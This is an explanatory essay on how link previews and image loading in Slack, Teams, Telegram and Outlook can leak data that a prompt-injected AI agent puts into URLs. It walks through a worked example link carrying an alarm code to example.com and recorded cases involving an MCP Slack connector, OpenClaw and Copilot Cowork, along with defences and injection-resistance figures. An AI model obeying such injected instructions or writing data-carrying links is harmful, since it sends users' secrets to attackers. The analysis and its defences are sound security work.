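# Who is responsible for security when an app displays an AI agent's output

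## How an agent's message can leak data when an app displays it

An AI agent is a language model, with the software around it, that reads data and takes actions such as posting messages or fetching web pages. Many people now talk to agents through chat and mail apps they already use, such as Slack, Teams, Telegram and Outlook. When an app displays an agent's message, it often does more than show the text. Chat apps commonly look up the links in a message to show a title and picture from each page, and mail apps may load images from other servers. Such a lookup is an automatic fetch, a network request that software makes without the user clicking anything, and the request can carry data out. A stranger who influences what an agent writes may therefore be able to use the app to send out private data, even if the agent never contacts the stranger.

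Several parties are involved when an app displays an agent's message. The agent builder writes and releases the agent or the connector it posts through. A connector is software that lets an agent use another service. Many connectors follow a common standard, the Model Context Protocol (MCP), and are called MCP servers. The rendering platform is the app that receives and displays the agent's output. The deploying organisation is the company or person who connects the agent to the platform and gives it access to data. Any of these parties could stop the leak, at least in part, and each has a plausible reason to leave the job to someone else. Judging those reasons requires knowing what each machine does between the agent's reply and the stranger's server.

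### How a document can give orders

OpenClaw, a popular open-source system, is an example of how an agent is built. *Agents of Chaos*, a paper on the risks of such systems, describes it as a framework that connects language models to persistent memory, tool execution, scheduling and messaging channels. This means it can keep notes between conversations, run programs, act at set times and reply in a chat window. The model itself only takes in text, called the context, and produces more text. The surrounding software assembles the context from the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the user's request, and any documents, pages or messages the agent has fetched.

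The model receives all of this as one stream, which is a weakness because a model cannot tell the system prompt from the rest of its context, as the security firm PromptArmor explained in *Data exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*. Developers can label the parts, and companies train their models to give a user's words more weight than a web page's, but this is a learned tendency that no code enforces. Prompt injection is text in a page, file or message that the model takes as an instruction although its user never gave it. PromptArmor credits Jon Cefalu with discovering the problem and Kai Greshake with the term "indirect prompt injection", which applies when the text reaches the model through something the agent reads.

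A person reading the same document may not notice the injected instructions. *Security Advisory*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, demonstrates an attack whose instructions are written in invisible characters in a source code file. Injections do not always work, but an attacker can put the same paragraph in a thousand documents and needs it to work only once. In *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), OpenAI treats the defence as an ongoing engineering problem and expects attackers to keep adapting.

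### What an address gives away

To open a page, software sends the site a request. According to http.dev's *HTTP Request*, the first line of the request contains a method such as GET, the target, and the protocol version. The target is the part of the address after the site's name. It includes the query string, which follows the question mark and holds details such as page numbers and search terms. The site needs the target to return the right page, so requesting an address also reveals it to the site. OpenAI notes that sites commonly log these addresses.

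A data-carrying link has private data written into its address, so requesting the link delivers the data to the site's owner. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security standards, has a rule for web developers, *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL*, which forbids private data in the parameters of an address because it would stay in the browser's history and in the logs of the server and any proxy on the way. The rule is meant to prevent careless leaks, but an attacker uses a data-carrying link specifically to get the data into a log.

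A server can log the address in a link even if it answers "not found". Encryption doesn't prevent the leak, because it hides the address from eavesdroppers along the way but not from the attacker, who receives the request. An address can be thousands of characters long, which is enough to hold a password or an access key.

### A worked example

Suppose an office manager uses an agent through the company's Slack. The agent has access to the company's internal notes, including one that gives a warehouse's alarm code, HERON-4417. The manager asks for a summary of a new supplier's brochure. Somebody has added a paragraph to the brochure, in white text on a white page, instructing any model that reads it to find the alarm code and end its reply with a link that has the code at the end of the address. The site here is example.com, a domain that IANA reserves for illustrations.

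A tool first converts the brochure into text. The output is only prose, so a virus scanner, which looks for malicious programs, finds nothing. The conversion tool also has no way to distinguish an unwanted paragraph from any other.

The model then receives the manager's request and the brochure, followed by the notes once it has looked them up. Looking up the alarm code breaks no access rule, because the agent acts with the manager's permissions and the manager is allowed to read that note. If the injection succeeds, the model writes a decent summary and ends it with an invitation to read more at `example.com/details?ref=HERON-4417`.

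The connector then receives the reply's text and the name of a Slack conversation, and there is nothing wrong with either. The reply is going to the person who requested it, who is entitled to know the code, so a check for secrets being sent to the wrong reader would let it through. The company may also run egress control on the agent's machine, which limits the outbound network requests a system may make. At this point, the only connection it registers is to Slack, which the company has approved.

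Slack receives a valid message containing a link from an app that the company installed. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* ("unfurling" means making link previews), Slack's servers have to fetch every address in a message to learn what kind of content it leads to. Query strings are common in addresses, and nothing in `ref=HERON-4417` distinguishes an alarm code from an order number, so Slack's preview robot makes the request.

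The attacker's server logs the request `GET /details?ref=HERON-4417` from Slackbot-LinkExpanding and returns a title and a picture of some shelving. The attacker already has the code when the manager opens Slack a minute later. The manager sees a useful summary with a link preview under it, and may never click the link.

Rehberger documented the essentials of this in August 2024. In Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, a test link goes to Slack through a webhook (an address at which Slack accepts messages from other software), and the robot's visit appears in the server's log. The programmer Simon Willison (2024), in *21st August 2024*, admitted that he hadn't thought of this route before, which suggests that it wasn't obvious even to people who followed prompt injection closely. It has since become better known, partly because PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from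 Agents in Messaging Apps* included a public test that people could run on their own agents.

### Who sends the request, and when

What triggers the request matters for preventing the leak, because it determines which machine contacts the attacker and whether a person has a chance to intervene. The attacker's log looks much the same whatever the trigger.

| Trigger | What the reader has to do | Which machine makes the request |
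|---|---|---|
| A click on the link | Click | The reader's own device |
| An image that loads with the message | Open the message | The reader's device, or the platform's servers if the app fetches images through a proxy |
| A link preview | Nothing; the fetch happens on delivery | Often the platform's servers; in some apps the sender's or the receiver's device |

In August 2024, PromptArmor reported a flaw in Slack AI, Slack's built-in assistant. According to Willison's summary in *20th August 2024*, an attacker could make the assistant show a link that sent private data to the attacker's server when the user clicked it. Requiring a click gives the user some chance to notice the attack, but the chance is slim because a link can show friendly words instead of its address, and few people study a query string before clicking.

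For an image to leak data, the reader only has to open the message. Whether the request for the image comes from the reader's device depends on the app. Slack uses a proxy, which benefits privacy because, as Slack explains, it hides detailed referrer information that can include the names of teams and projects. But the proxy still requests the image from the address in the message, so if that address contains the alarm code, the attacker gets the code from Slack's server instead of the manager's laptop. Embrace The Red also found that a single image link brings visits from three separate Slack robots, so images and previews are less distinct on Slack.

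Link previews vary the most from app to app. Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020) tested popular chat apps and sorted them by which machine fetches the link. Slack, Discord, LinkedIn, Zoom and several others used their own servers. In iMessage, WhatsApp, Viber and Signal (if the user had previews on), the sender's phone built the preview and attached it to the message. In two apps that Mysk didn't name, the receiver's phone opened the link as soon as the message came into view. Positive Security's *MS Teams*, another older test, suggests that Microsoft's servers fetch the previews in Teams. When Mysk sent a link to a 2.6-gigabyte file through Instagram, several Facebook servers immediately began downloading it, and together they took about 24.7 gigabytes. Any of these apps may have changed since the tests.

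Mysk considered the receiver's phone the worst place to make a link preview, because fetching the link reveals the phone's internet address and therefore its rough location. It considered the sender's phone the best place, assuming that whoever sends a link trusts it. This ranking helps little when the link contains secret data, because any machine that requests the link sends the data with it. The assumption about trust also fails if the sender is an agent under a stranger's influence.

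Several precautions that platforms already take with link previews don't prevent this kind of leak. Slack's robot reads as little of each page as it can, and in Mysk's tests Discord stopped downloading at 15 megabytes and Slack at 50, but these limits apply only to incoming data, and the leaked data goes out in the request. Slack also keeps each response for around 30 minutes, which may prevent a second request for the same address, but the first request is enough to leak the data.

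An app may have sent a request to a linked page even if no preview appears. Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* lists missing preview data on the page as one reason a link may not expand, and Slack would almost certainly have to fetch the page to find out that the data is missing.

### Two assumptions that meet in one message

People who build agents understandably tend to treat the output as text. In Embrace The Red's sample code for posting a message from a Slack app, the message has only a text field. The same text would do nothing in a plain text file, but Slack by default unfurls, or previews, links in messages from both users and apps. A builder who uses this code therefore gets previews without choosing them, and has to add two settings to the message to turn them off.

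Platforms designed previews for links that a person chose to share. PromptArmor makes this point about messaging apps in general, and Slack's own wording supports it. Slack's help page introduces previews with "When you share a link", and its developer documentation starts with users posting messages. Slack is most explicit on a page for website owners who have found its robots in their logs, where it explains why the preview robot ignores robots.txt, the file that sites use to turn crawlers away. Slack does not consider the robot a crawler because it does not follow links and is "acting on behalf of a human".

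For years that was a fair description. Someone who pastes a link into a chat has usually looked at the page and has no motive to leak their employer's alarm code. Older apps posted links too, but mostly ones that a developer had planned for, such as the address of a support ticket. But an agent under prompt injection posts a link that a stranger has in effect written. Slack now advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages from a language model, but it has not changed the default.

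Both assumptions are correct, since the agent returned only text and the platform only made a preview. Testing the agent alone, in a window that makes no automatic fetches, would reveal no leak, and neither would testing previews with links from colleagues. The fault appears when someone connects the two, often a deploying organisation that wrote neither piece of software.

### What "responsibility gap" means here

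Here, a responsibility gap means a harm that some component could prevent but that no party considers its job to prevent. Philosophers use the phrase in a different sense, which comes from a 2004 article by Andreas Matthias.

In *The responsibility gap*, Matthias starts from the principle that people are responsible for an outcome only if they had enough control over it. The operator of an ordinary machine has that control as long as the machine works as the manual describes, and the manufacturer is responsible for defects. This division is hard to apply to machines that learn. Matthias imagines a lift that adapts to the traffic in an office tower and one day leaves an executive waiting for half an hour on the 34th floor, at considerable cost. The manufacturer could not have predicted this, because the lift had altered its own program since leaving the factory. Nobody had enough control to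 be fairly blamed, so society must either do without such machines, which Matthias thinks is unrealistic, or accept that sometimes no one can be held responsible for what they do.

*The AI Criminal Mastermind* (2026) extends the argument to AI agents, whose developers cannot predict what they will do. Some of this applies to the alarm code. No one at the company that built the agent could have predicted whether this model would fall for this paragraph. But a builder can stop the request by switching previews off, and a platform can stop it by not fetching links from agents, without either knowing which message is the bad one. Slack can evidently tell apps' messages from people's, since it does not invite other apps to supply a custom preview when a message came from an app. Several people therefore had control in Matthias's sense, but they had no agreement about who should use it.

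Santoni de Sio and Mecacci (2021), in *Four Responsibility Gaps with Artificial Intelligence*, argue that Matthias described only one kind of gap, in culpability, and that there are others in moral accountability, public accountability and what they call active responsibility. Active responsibility is the obligation of people who design or use technology to prevent certain harms. A gap arises when they are not sufficiently aware of this obligation, or not able or motivated to meet it. One of the paper's examples is a manager at a technology company who sincerely believes that limiting a product's damage to people's privacy is not part of the job. This gap is close to the one in the preview case and differs mostly in emphasis. Santoni de Sio and Mecacci focus on what individuals know and are inclined to do, whereas an alarm code can leak in a preview even when two conscientious teams have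 each secured everything they consider their own.

The "problem of many hands" arises when so many people contribute to an outcome that no individual is clearly to blame. The problem is older than AI and can occur in a bureaucracy without it. A preview leak has fewer contributors, and we can list them.

Some philosophers doubt that responsibility gaps deserve much worry. *The Accountability Horizon* (2026) calls them deflationists, as Santoni de Sio and Mecacci do, and contrasts them with fatalists such as Matthias. According to Santoni de Sio and Mecacci, Thomas Simpson and Vincent Müller compare AI with bridges and buildings. Society can accept that a bridge sometimes collapses without anyone being culpable, provided that everyone took all reasonable precautions and nobody could reasonably have prevented the accident. The case of the office manager's alarm code does not meet that condition,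 because nobody took an available precaution that, on Slack, would have required two lines of code from the builder.

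## Three recorded cases and what each party did afterwards

The warehouse and its alarm code are fictional, but researchers have produced the same kind of leak in products that people use at work. Three of these cases have enough public documentation to show what each party did afterwards. The data belonged to researchers or volunteers, and none of the published accounts describes a theft by a real attacker. The cases are therefore weak evidence of how much damage such leaks have done, but they are more useful for learning how companies respond once someone demonstrates a leak.

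### Anthropic's Slack connector

Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, launched MCP with a set of reference connectors and published these working examples on the code-sharing site GitHub. The one that connected agents to Slack worked with both Anthropic's products and other companies'. Embrace The Red mentions Claude Desktop, Claude Code, and the programming tools Windsurf and VS Code.

The connector left Slack's link previews on. Rehberger reported it to Anthropic on 27 May 2025, nine months after documenting the general danger. In one demonstration, a user asks Claude Desktop to analyse a document and post a summary for the team. The document contains a prompt injection, so the agent also looks up the latest message in another Slack channel, puts it in a URL and posts the URL. Slack's preview bot then delivers the message to Rehberger's server.

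In the demonstration with invisible characters in a source code file, Claude Code took an access key from a developer's .env file, where programmers commonly keep the passwords and keys their software needs. The key had never been in Slack. The connector could leak anything the agent could read, including files on the user's computer and data from other connectors.

Most agents ask the user for confirmation before they use a tool like this one, but Rehberger suspects that many people turn the confirmations off as they come to rely on the agent. People seem likely to do this for Slack posts. A company can restrict the connector to a single private channel, and a developer may then reason that even the worst message would reach only a few colleagues, who could delete it.

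This reasoning holds for the colleagues, because a channel's membership determines who can read a message. But membership doesn't affect which websites Slack's robot visits to build a preview. With previews on, an agent with permission to post in one private channel can also send a line of text to any web server through Slack. The developer has allowed both but knows only about the posting. A confirmation prompt would at least have shown a person the link before Slack fetched it.

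Anthropic archived the connector on 29 May, two days after the report. Rehberger could not tell whether the report prompted this, and it may well not have, because Anthropic retired many of its reference connectors at about the same time. Archiving ended maintenance, so Anthropic did not plan to fix the flaw, although the fix takes two settings. Anthropic told Rehberger it did not object to publication.

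Retiring the connector did not protect the people who already had it, and new users kept arriving. Rehberger found more than 14,000 downloads in a recent week and inferred that there might be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations. The connector was still in use, but his estimate is loose. Automated systems often download the same package again every time they rebuild a program, so there could be far fewer installations than downloads.

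As far as Rehberger could tell, Anthropic did not intend to issue a CVE, a numbered entry in a public catalogue of security flaws. Companies use these numbers to check whether they run software with a known flaw, so a flaw without one is easy to miss. VulnCheck, a security firm that can assign the numbers, issued CVE-2025-34072 instead. The entry in the American government's vulnerability database, NIST's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025), dates from 2 July 2025, five weeks after the report.

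The entry describes a vulnerability in "Anthropic's deprecated Slack Model Context Protocol (MCP) Server". VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* lists all default deployments of that connector as affected and credits Rehberger under the pseudonym wunderwuzzi. The catalogue attributes the flaw to the connector, although according to its description Slack's robots send the request that leaks the data. Rehberger's account of the disclosure mentions only Anthropic.

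People who agreed on how the flaw worked still disagreed about how serious it was. On the usual 0-to-10 scale, the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), VulnCheck gave it 9.3 (critical) and Rehberger gave it 7.5 (high). NIST had not published a score. Out of curiosity, Rehberger also asked several chatbots to score it. ChatGPT gave 9.1, Grok 9.3 and Gemini 8.7, while Claude returned an error message.

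Rehberger did not publish the inputs behind the 7.5, but VulnCheck's inputs help explain why its score is so high. CVSS version 4.0 separates harm to the vulnerable system from harm to other systems connected with it. For the connector, VulnCheck entered a high loss of confidentiality and no loss of integrity or availability, which fits a leak. For the other systems, it entered a high loss of all three. The confidentiality rating is easy to understand, since the agent may fetch secrets from anywhere. The integrity and availability ratings are harder to justify, because a preview request sends data out without altering or disabling anything. An attacker would need a second attack, perhaps using a stolen key, to do either.

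The scorers also disagreed about whether the victim takes part. VulnCheck entered no user interaction, but Gemini's inputs included some, presumably because a person has to give the agent the poisoned document. CVSS was built for flaws with a definite location, and its inputs are hard to fill in when one company's software writes the address and another's requests it.

In the end, whoever was running the connector had to fix it. Rehberger advised companies to find out who had installed it and patch it themselves, or to use a connector from the maker of the product it connects to, which is more likely to receive security fixes. The advice is sensible, but it depends on a company knowing that one of its developers installed a free connector months earlier.

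### PromptArmor's test of agents and apps

The advisory concerned one connector, but the mechanism isn't specific to Slack or Anthropic. PromptArmor opened its public test to other combinations of agent and app in February 2026.

PromptArmor set up a website that logged visits from link-preview bots and any data in the URL. One of the published log entries contains a name and an access key. An entry could show which bot had visited, such as Slack's or Telegram's, but not which agent had written the link, so PromptArmor let people "claim" their entries and state which agent they had used. People could also report agents whose links had not triggered a preview.

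PromptArmor found that OpenClaw leaked data through Telegram in its default configuration. The data stopped arriving when a user turned off link previews, which takes one line in OpenClaw's configuration file. In *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, Apostol lists Teams with Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents, and Slack with certain bots among the other exposed combinations, and also names Discord as an affected app.

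PromptArmor also published a list of combinations that people had reported as safe. Some safe combinations are to be expected. Mysk found that in some apps, such as WhatsApp and Signal, the sender's phone builds the preview. When an agent sends the message, its connector takes the phone's place, and if the connector doesn't build previews, there may be no automatic fetch. This protection would be accidental, and a later update that added previews to the agent's messages would remove it.

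The results are counts of what volunteers saw, and they can't be turned into rates because nobody knows how many people tried each combination. If Teams appears often in the logs, the reason may be that many of the testers use it at work. One tester could produce dozens of entries in an afternoon. People who had heard that their agent was vulnerable were probably more likely to test it, and those who saw nothing happen had less reason to report it.

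A recorded fetch also proves more than a report that nothing happened. It shows that the combination can leak under at least one configuration, provided the volunteer named the right agent. A report that nothing happened might mean the app is safe, but it might equally mean that the volunteer's employer had turned previews off, or that the agent declined to write the link that day. The logs cover only the final stage of the attack, in which an app fetches a link that an agent has written, so they don't show how often an injection would get the agent to write it.

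None of this matters much for OpenClaw on Telegram, because PromptArmor identified the default itself and anyone could repeat the test. But OpenClaw's setup guide, *Telegram*, still listed link previews as on by default in late August 2026, half a year after the test.

The same guide describes strict defaults for incoming messages. A stranger who writes to the agent on Telegram has to be approved with a pairing code, which expires after an hour. The agent ignores group chats until its owner lists them, and if the Telegram settings are missing, OpenClaw blocks groups instead of admitting them. The guide explains at length who may give the agent orders but has only two sentences on link previews. The pairing code doesn't stop an attacker who plants an injection in a web page, because they never have to write to the agent on Telegram and can collect the data through the preview.

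PromptArmor's article doesn't mention a private report to OpenClaw, Telegram or any other company. It warned the public and described a setting that users could change themselves. Apostol quotes no reply from the companies. Readers disagreed about whose problem it was. On the discussion site Hacker News, one commenter called it "a protocol-level issue, not a framework bug" and recommended network rules that block unexpected outbound traffic from the agent. Such rules would miss the leak whenever the chat company's server fetches the preview, as in the alarm code example. Another commenter explained the difficulty more clearly, noting that the agent only includes a link in its reply, so it makes no tool call for which it could ask permission.

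### Copilot Cowork's messages to its own user

Microsoft built both the Copilot Cowork agent and the apps that display its messages, whereas OpenClaw's developers don't run Telegram and Anthropic doesn't run Slack. Cowork works inside Microsoft 365, where it searches a company's files, writes documents, sends mail through Outlook and posts messages in Teams, all with its user's permissions. Microsoft also built the storage that holds the files, while Anthropic supplied the language models that Cowork used at the time.

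Microsoft's *Application card*, which describes the product and its risks, calls the user approval system Cowork's "primary safety mechanism". Cowork is supposed to pause and show the user a preview before it sends an email or posts a message. Microsoft made the same promise in its instructions for users.

PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated an exception in which Cowork sent a message immediately if the only recipient was its own user. Users had no setting to change this. Willison (2026) drew attention to the finding on 26 May, under the same title.

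At least one customer had already run into the exception, with no reason to worry about it. In *Cowork can't send emails?*, posted on Microsoft's forum on 14 April, VirginiaH1 (2026) asked why Cowork could send test emails to its user but to nobody else. The post quotes Cowork's explanation that "self-sends appear to be auto-approved". A model's account of the software around it is poor evidence by itself, but PromptArmor's tests support this one. The forum replies dealt with the missing approval prompt for other recipients, which began working within two days.

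Exempting messages to oneself from approval is unsafe for the same reason as in the private Slack channel, because the app that displays the message fetches outside content automatically. Here the fetch comes from images. Messages from Cowork could contain images from outside servers, and Outlook and Teams requested them when the user opened the message. The exemption is still understandable, since a person who asks for a weekly summary by email doesn't want to approve its delivery, and the message has no other recipient.

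PromptArmor put its injection in a skill, a file of instructions that Cowork follows to do a particular task. People find skills online and upload them as they would a spreadsheet template. Cowork loads them automatically from a folder in the user's OneDrive. Administrators have little oversight of the skills there, and Microsoft does not validate the ones users add. The injection took up five of the 81 lines in PromptArmor's file.

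The user then asked Cowork to go over the week's work, and Cowork opened the skill. The injected lines presented the attacker's site as a document preview service, so Cowork fetched a "pre-authenticated" download link for each file, which works for anyone who has it. It put those links into the addresses of images and sent the images to the user in a Teams message. When the user opened Teams, the app requested the images and the attacker received the download links. The files in the test contained financial and personal data.

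The download links make this leak much larger than the one in the alarm code example. A company's accounts are too long to fit in an address, but a download link fits and gives the attacker the whole file.

The user had little chance of noticing. Cowork displays its steps as it works, but PromptArmor found that it did not show the content of the Teams message, even when the user clicked on the step. The user could inspect the message only by opening it in Teams, which triggered the leak.

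The attack succeeded in all five of PromptArmor's trials, however the user worded the request, as long as Cowork opened the skill. Five trials is a small sample, since an attack that works only 55% of the time would succeed in all five about one time in twenty. The injection was also in a skill, which is meant to contain instructions for the agent, so the result may not hold for an injection in an ordinary email. But the attack would still be a threat if it worked much less often.

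A more capable model did not prevent the attack. PromptArmor first let Cowork choose between two Claude models, then repeated the attack with the stronger one, Opus 4.7, using the same injection. Opus 4.7 searched more thoroughly for recent documents and so leaked more of them, including every document from that week's earlier Cowork sessions. The user also doesn't have to be present when the agent runs, because Cowork can repeat a task on a schedule, and a weekly review is a natural task to schedule. A poisoned skill could then send out new links every week, for as long as the user kept opening the messages.

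Microsoft had tested whether an attacker could manipulate Cowork into harmful actions. Its card gives the examples of sending emails to unintended recipients, acting without proper approval and getting around permission boundaries. A message to the user goes to the intended recipient and stays within the user's permissions. The documentation required approval for the message but the product didn't ask for it, so whether it lacked "proper approval" depends on which of the two one goes by. The whole sequence could easily have passed a test that covered only the agent's actions, because the leak occurs later, in Teams or Outlook.

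Microsoft does not appear to have explained how the exception came about, so any account of how the work was divided inside the company is guesswork. Whoever exempted these messages from approval needed to know how two other products load images, and Microsoft's ownership of all three did not guarantee that anyone would check. A gap in responsibility can evidently exist between teams as well as between firms. It should be easier to close inside one firm, because one manager has authority over both teams.

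PromptArmor presented the attack as a design risk that users should know they were accepting, rather than as a specific bug. That may have influenced what happened next. Microsoft does fix leaks in this family of products when researchers report them as bugs. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Controlled by Attacker, Bypassing Sandbox* concerns a separate flaw that PromptArmor reported on 24 June 2026, and Microsoft confirmed on 19 August that it had dealt with the flaw. Between September and November, Microsoft also patched three ways of extracting data from Microsoft 365 Copilot, one of which used image addresses, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026).

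There is no comparable public record of a fix for the messages that Cowork sends to its own user. Microsoft's release log for the product, by ilyagrebnov (2026), in *(Co)work in Progress*, runs to 24 August and has no entry about approval for such messages or about the images in them. Microsoft may have made a change without announcing it, since a log of new features would not usually list security fixes. The log does record that Cowork is now generally available and can start tasks when a particular email or Teams message arrives. Microsoft has these tasks prepare drafts for approval by default, a reasonable precaution, but the log does not specify whether a message to the user needs approval.

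Microsoft's documentation describes this approval inconsistently. In June, after PromptArmor's disclosure, the application card still described approval for sending emails and posting messages without mentioning an exception. According to the training page *Explore how Cowork works*, such actions "typically" pause for approval. According to the support page *Get started with Cowork*, which was online in August and may apply only to personal accounts, Cowork requires approval for "actions involving other people, such as sending emails or messages". That wording is compatible with the exception. If it reflects a deliberate change, Microsoft revised the description to match the product instead of changing the product.

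An administrator at a company that uses Cowork can block downloads from a SharePoint site, so that Cowork can't obtain the links. But people then can't download, print or sync those files, or open them in Word and Excel, and have to read them in a browser. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) also recommends that an administrator review every skill before anyone uses it, and that companies forbid employees to choose "Don't ask again" when Cowork requests approval. Reviewing skills would help against this attack if the reviewer noticed the five bad lines among 81. Forbidding "Don't ask again" would not help, because Cowork never requested approval.

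The table sets out the three cases. For PromptArmor's test, it covers only OpenClaw on Telegram, the combination with the best documentation.

| Case | What triggered the request | Where a check was missing | Who acted | Remedy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's Slack connector, 2025 | A link preview, on delivery | The connector left previews on, and Slack fetched the link | Anthropic retired the connector; VulnCheck issued the CVE | No patch from Anthropic; users edit the code or replace the connector |
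| OpenClaw on Telegram, 2026 | A link preview, on delivery | OpenClaw left previews on, and Telegram fetched the link | PromptArmor published a test and a safe configuration | Users turn previews off; the default was unchanged in August 2026 |
| Copilot Cowork, 2026 | Images, when the user opened the message | Cowork skipped approval for messages to its user, and Outlook and Teams loaded outside images | PromptArmor published a warning; Microsoft announced no change in its release log to August 2026 | Administrators block file downloads and review skills |

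## The view that the agent's builder should make the output safe

In each of these cases, a change to the agent or its connector would have stopped the leak without any help from the app that displayed the message. That is one reason to make the agent's builder responsible. A stronger reason is that the builder has information the platform lacks. From the message Slack receives, `ref=HERON-4417` could be an order number, but the builder's software had given the model the note containing the alarm code seconds earlier. The software had also given the model the brochure, which came from outside the company. The builder also knows that a model wrote the reply, and the builder's code controls where it is posted.

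Web developers already follow a similar rule. A site that displays visitors' comments has to neutralise any code in them, because a browser would otherwise run that code as if the site's owner had written it. On this view, an agent's reply is like a visitor's comment, and whoever passes it on should first make it safe for the program that will display it.

Slack largely takes this position in the app security page of its developer guidance. It recommends turning link previews off by default and disabling them whenever a message contains addresses that a model may have written. It also suggests an allowlist of the outside domains an app may contact, with all others blocked. Slack reasons that a person would have to find sensitive data and copy it into a message by hand, whereas an attacker can prompt a model to do both in one reply.

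The same page is misleading about who makes the request. Slack's guide to unfurling explains that Slack's own servers fetch the link for an ordinary preview, but in the security page's scenario, "the app" contacts the attacker's site once previews are on. A developer who relied on the security page might search the app's network log for a request that isn't there, or try to block it with egress controls on the app's machine, which it never passes through.

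Slack also builds agents, and it checks their output. It lists URL filtering and validation of the output's format among the guardrails for its AI features, although it presents the filtering as a protection against phishing.

### Turning previews off

Slack has two link preview settings for each message. `unfurl_links` covers links to pages that are mostly text, and `unfurl_media` covers links to images, video and audio. A builder who turns off only `unfurl_links` still allows previews of pictures, so an attacker can serve a picture. Slack also classifies a link by fetching it. With one setting still on, it presumably requests every link in the message to find out whether the setting applies, and that request leaks the data. Slack tells developers to set both to false to stop the fetch.

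Slack's guide is inconsistent about what happens if a builder sets neither. According to its text, Slack unfurls all links in messages from users and apps by default. But in one of its examples, a link to a text page won't unfurl unless `unfurl_links` is true. A builder who tried the example and saw no preview might conclude that Slack hadn't fetched the page, when it probably had fetched it to classify it.

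The settings also apply to one message at a time, so the builder has to include them everywhere the software posts. Slack mentions both the call that creates a message and the one that updates it. The update call is easy to overlook in an agent that displays its reply as the model writes it, since such an agent may edit the same message many times. Builders who let the model lay out a message with Block Kit, Slack's format for messages with buttons and pictures, also have to check the media links in it, because Slack unfurls those too.

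Telegram's documentation for bot developers describes an equivalent option, `link_preview_options`, with an `is_disabled` field that turns the preview off. Another field sets the address to preview. If the bot leaves it empty, Telegram uses the first address in the text, so an attacker only needs the injected link to come first. As a compromise, the builder can set this field to a known page and keep a preview that doesn't depend on the model's links. But the field's description leaves open whether Telegram contacts the other addresses anyway, so turning the preview off is safer.

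When previews are off, readers lose only the title and picture, and the link still works. But if the office manager clicks it, the attacker still gets the alarm code.

### Changing or removing the links

To stop clicks as well, the builder has to alter the reply, which has bigger drawbacks. Deleting every link is easy to program and may be acceptable for an agent that only summarises internal notes. But if the agent does research on the web, readers need the links to check its answer, and without them they have to trust the model or repeat the search.

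Milder changes are less reliable. Cutting off everything after the question mark removes `ref=HERON-4417`, but an attacker can ask for the code in the path instead, as in `example.com/HERON-4417`. It also breaks ordinary links that need a query string. Removing the `https://` prevents unfurling in Slack, which only unfurls addresses that include it. But readers then have to copy legitimate addresses into a browser, and copying a malicious one still leaks the data. Some apps also turn a bare domain name back into a link, so this would need testing on each platform.

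An allowlist lets the app keep links to the company's own systems and a few trusted sites. Slack suggests that the app block or report any other address the model writes. Reporting seems worthwhile because an unexpected domain in a reply may be the first sign of a prompt injection. An allowlist is less suitable for agents whose users want links from anywhere on the web.

An agent that posts only plain text can still leak data, because apps such as Slack preview links in a message's ordinary text field. The measure works only if the text contains no address that the app will recognise. Dropping formatting does remove embedded images, through which data could leave Copilot Cowork, but readers also lose tables and charts.

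A builder can often avoid these losses by not letting the model write addresses. The software already has the address of every page it retrieved, so the model can refer to a page by number and ordinary code can insert the matching link. An injection could still influence which of these links appears, but it couldn't add the alarm code to one. This takes more work than changing two settings and doesn't suit an agent that has to construct new addresses, such as a link to a filtered search, but it would be worth the extra work for most answers that cite sources.

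### Training the model to resist

The builder can also try to stop the model from obeying the injection. *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2026), a review of safety methods for agents, reports that training a model to favour trusted instructions reduces the risk without eliminating it, and that most evaluations tested models on their own rather than as part of working agents. The studies also use different attacks and definitions of success, so their success rates are hard to compare.

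Anthropic has published the most detailed figures. In 2026 it adopted a test of indirect prompt injection developed with the security firm Gray Swan and the British and American government institutes for AI security and standards. According to TechFeed, the test has 28 scenarios in coding, tool use and operating graphical interfaces, with 1,130 attacks. It replaced an older test on which Claude models had scored almost perfectly.

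| Model | Test | Success in one attempt | Success with repeated attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Earlier Gray Swan benchmark | 4.7% | 33.6% within 10; 63% within 100 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Graphical interface, no added safeguards | 17.8% | 78.6% within 200 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | Restricted coding environment | 0% | 0% within 200 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | New test with Gray Swan | 0.5% | 5.5% within 15 |
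| Claude Opus 5 | New test with Gray Swan | 0.2% | 2.0% within 15 |

The Opus 4.5 figures come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. The Opus 4.6 figures come from VentureBeat, which also reported that added safeguards lowered the 78.6% figure only to 57.1%. In the two Opus 4.6 rows, the model never failed in the coding environment but failed most of the time when it operated a graphical interface and the attacker could keep trying.

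Opus 5, from July 2026, resisted attacks better than its predecessors. Anthropic also measured an attack success rate of zero for its browser agent across 129 scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. A more capable model is not always more resistant. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5 ranks the model below Fable 5 in overall capability, yet attackers with 15 attempts succeeded slightly more often against Fable 5, at 2.8%.

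These figures don't cover the two newer models that Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced in November. Builders who use other companies' models have had less information. In a comparison of the models available in spring 2026, VentureBeat found that OpenAI gave a single score for GPT-5.5, based on known attacks through connectors, and that Google gave no injection results for Gemini 3.x.

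These rates may not carry over to data-carrying links. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition with 41 scenarios, built with the UK AI Security Institute and several AI companies. The injections were in places an attacker could plausibly reach, such as code comments and product reviews. The injected instructions were for actions a user would clearly not want, such as marking an email about a contract deadline as read or adding a backdoor to a program. A "read more" link under an accurate summary looks much more innocent, so a model that has learned to refuse sabotage might still write one.

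### Why a low rate is less reassuring against an attacker

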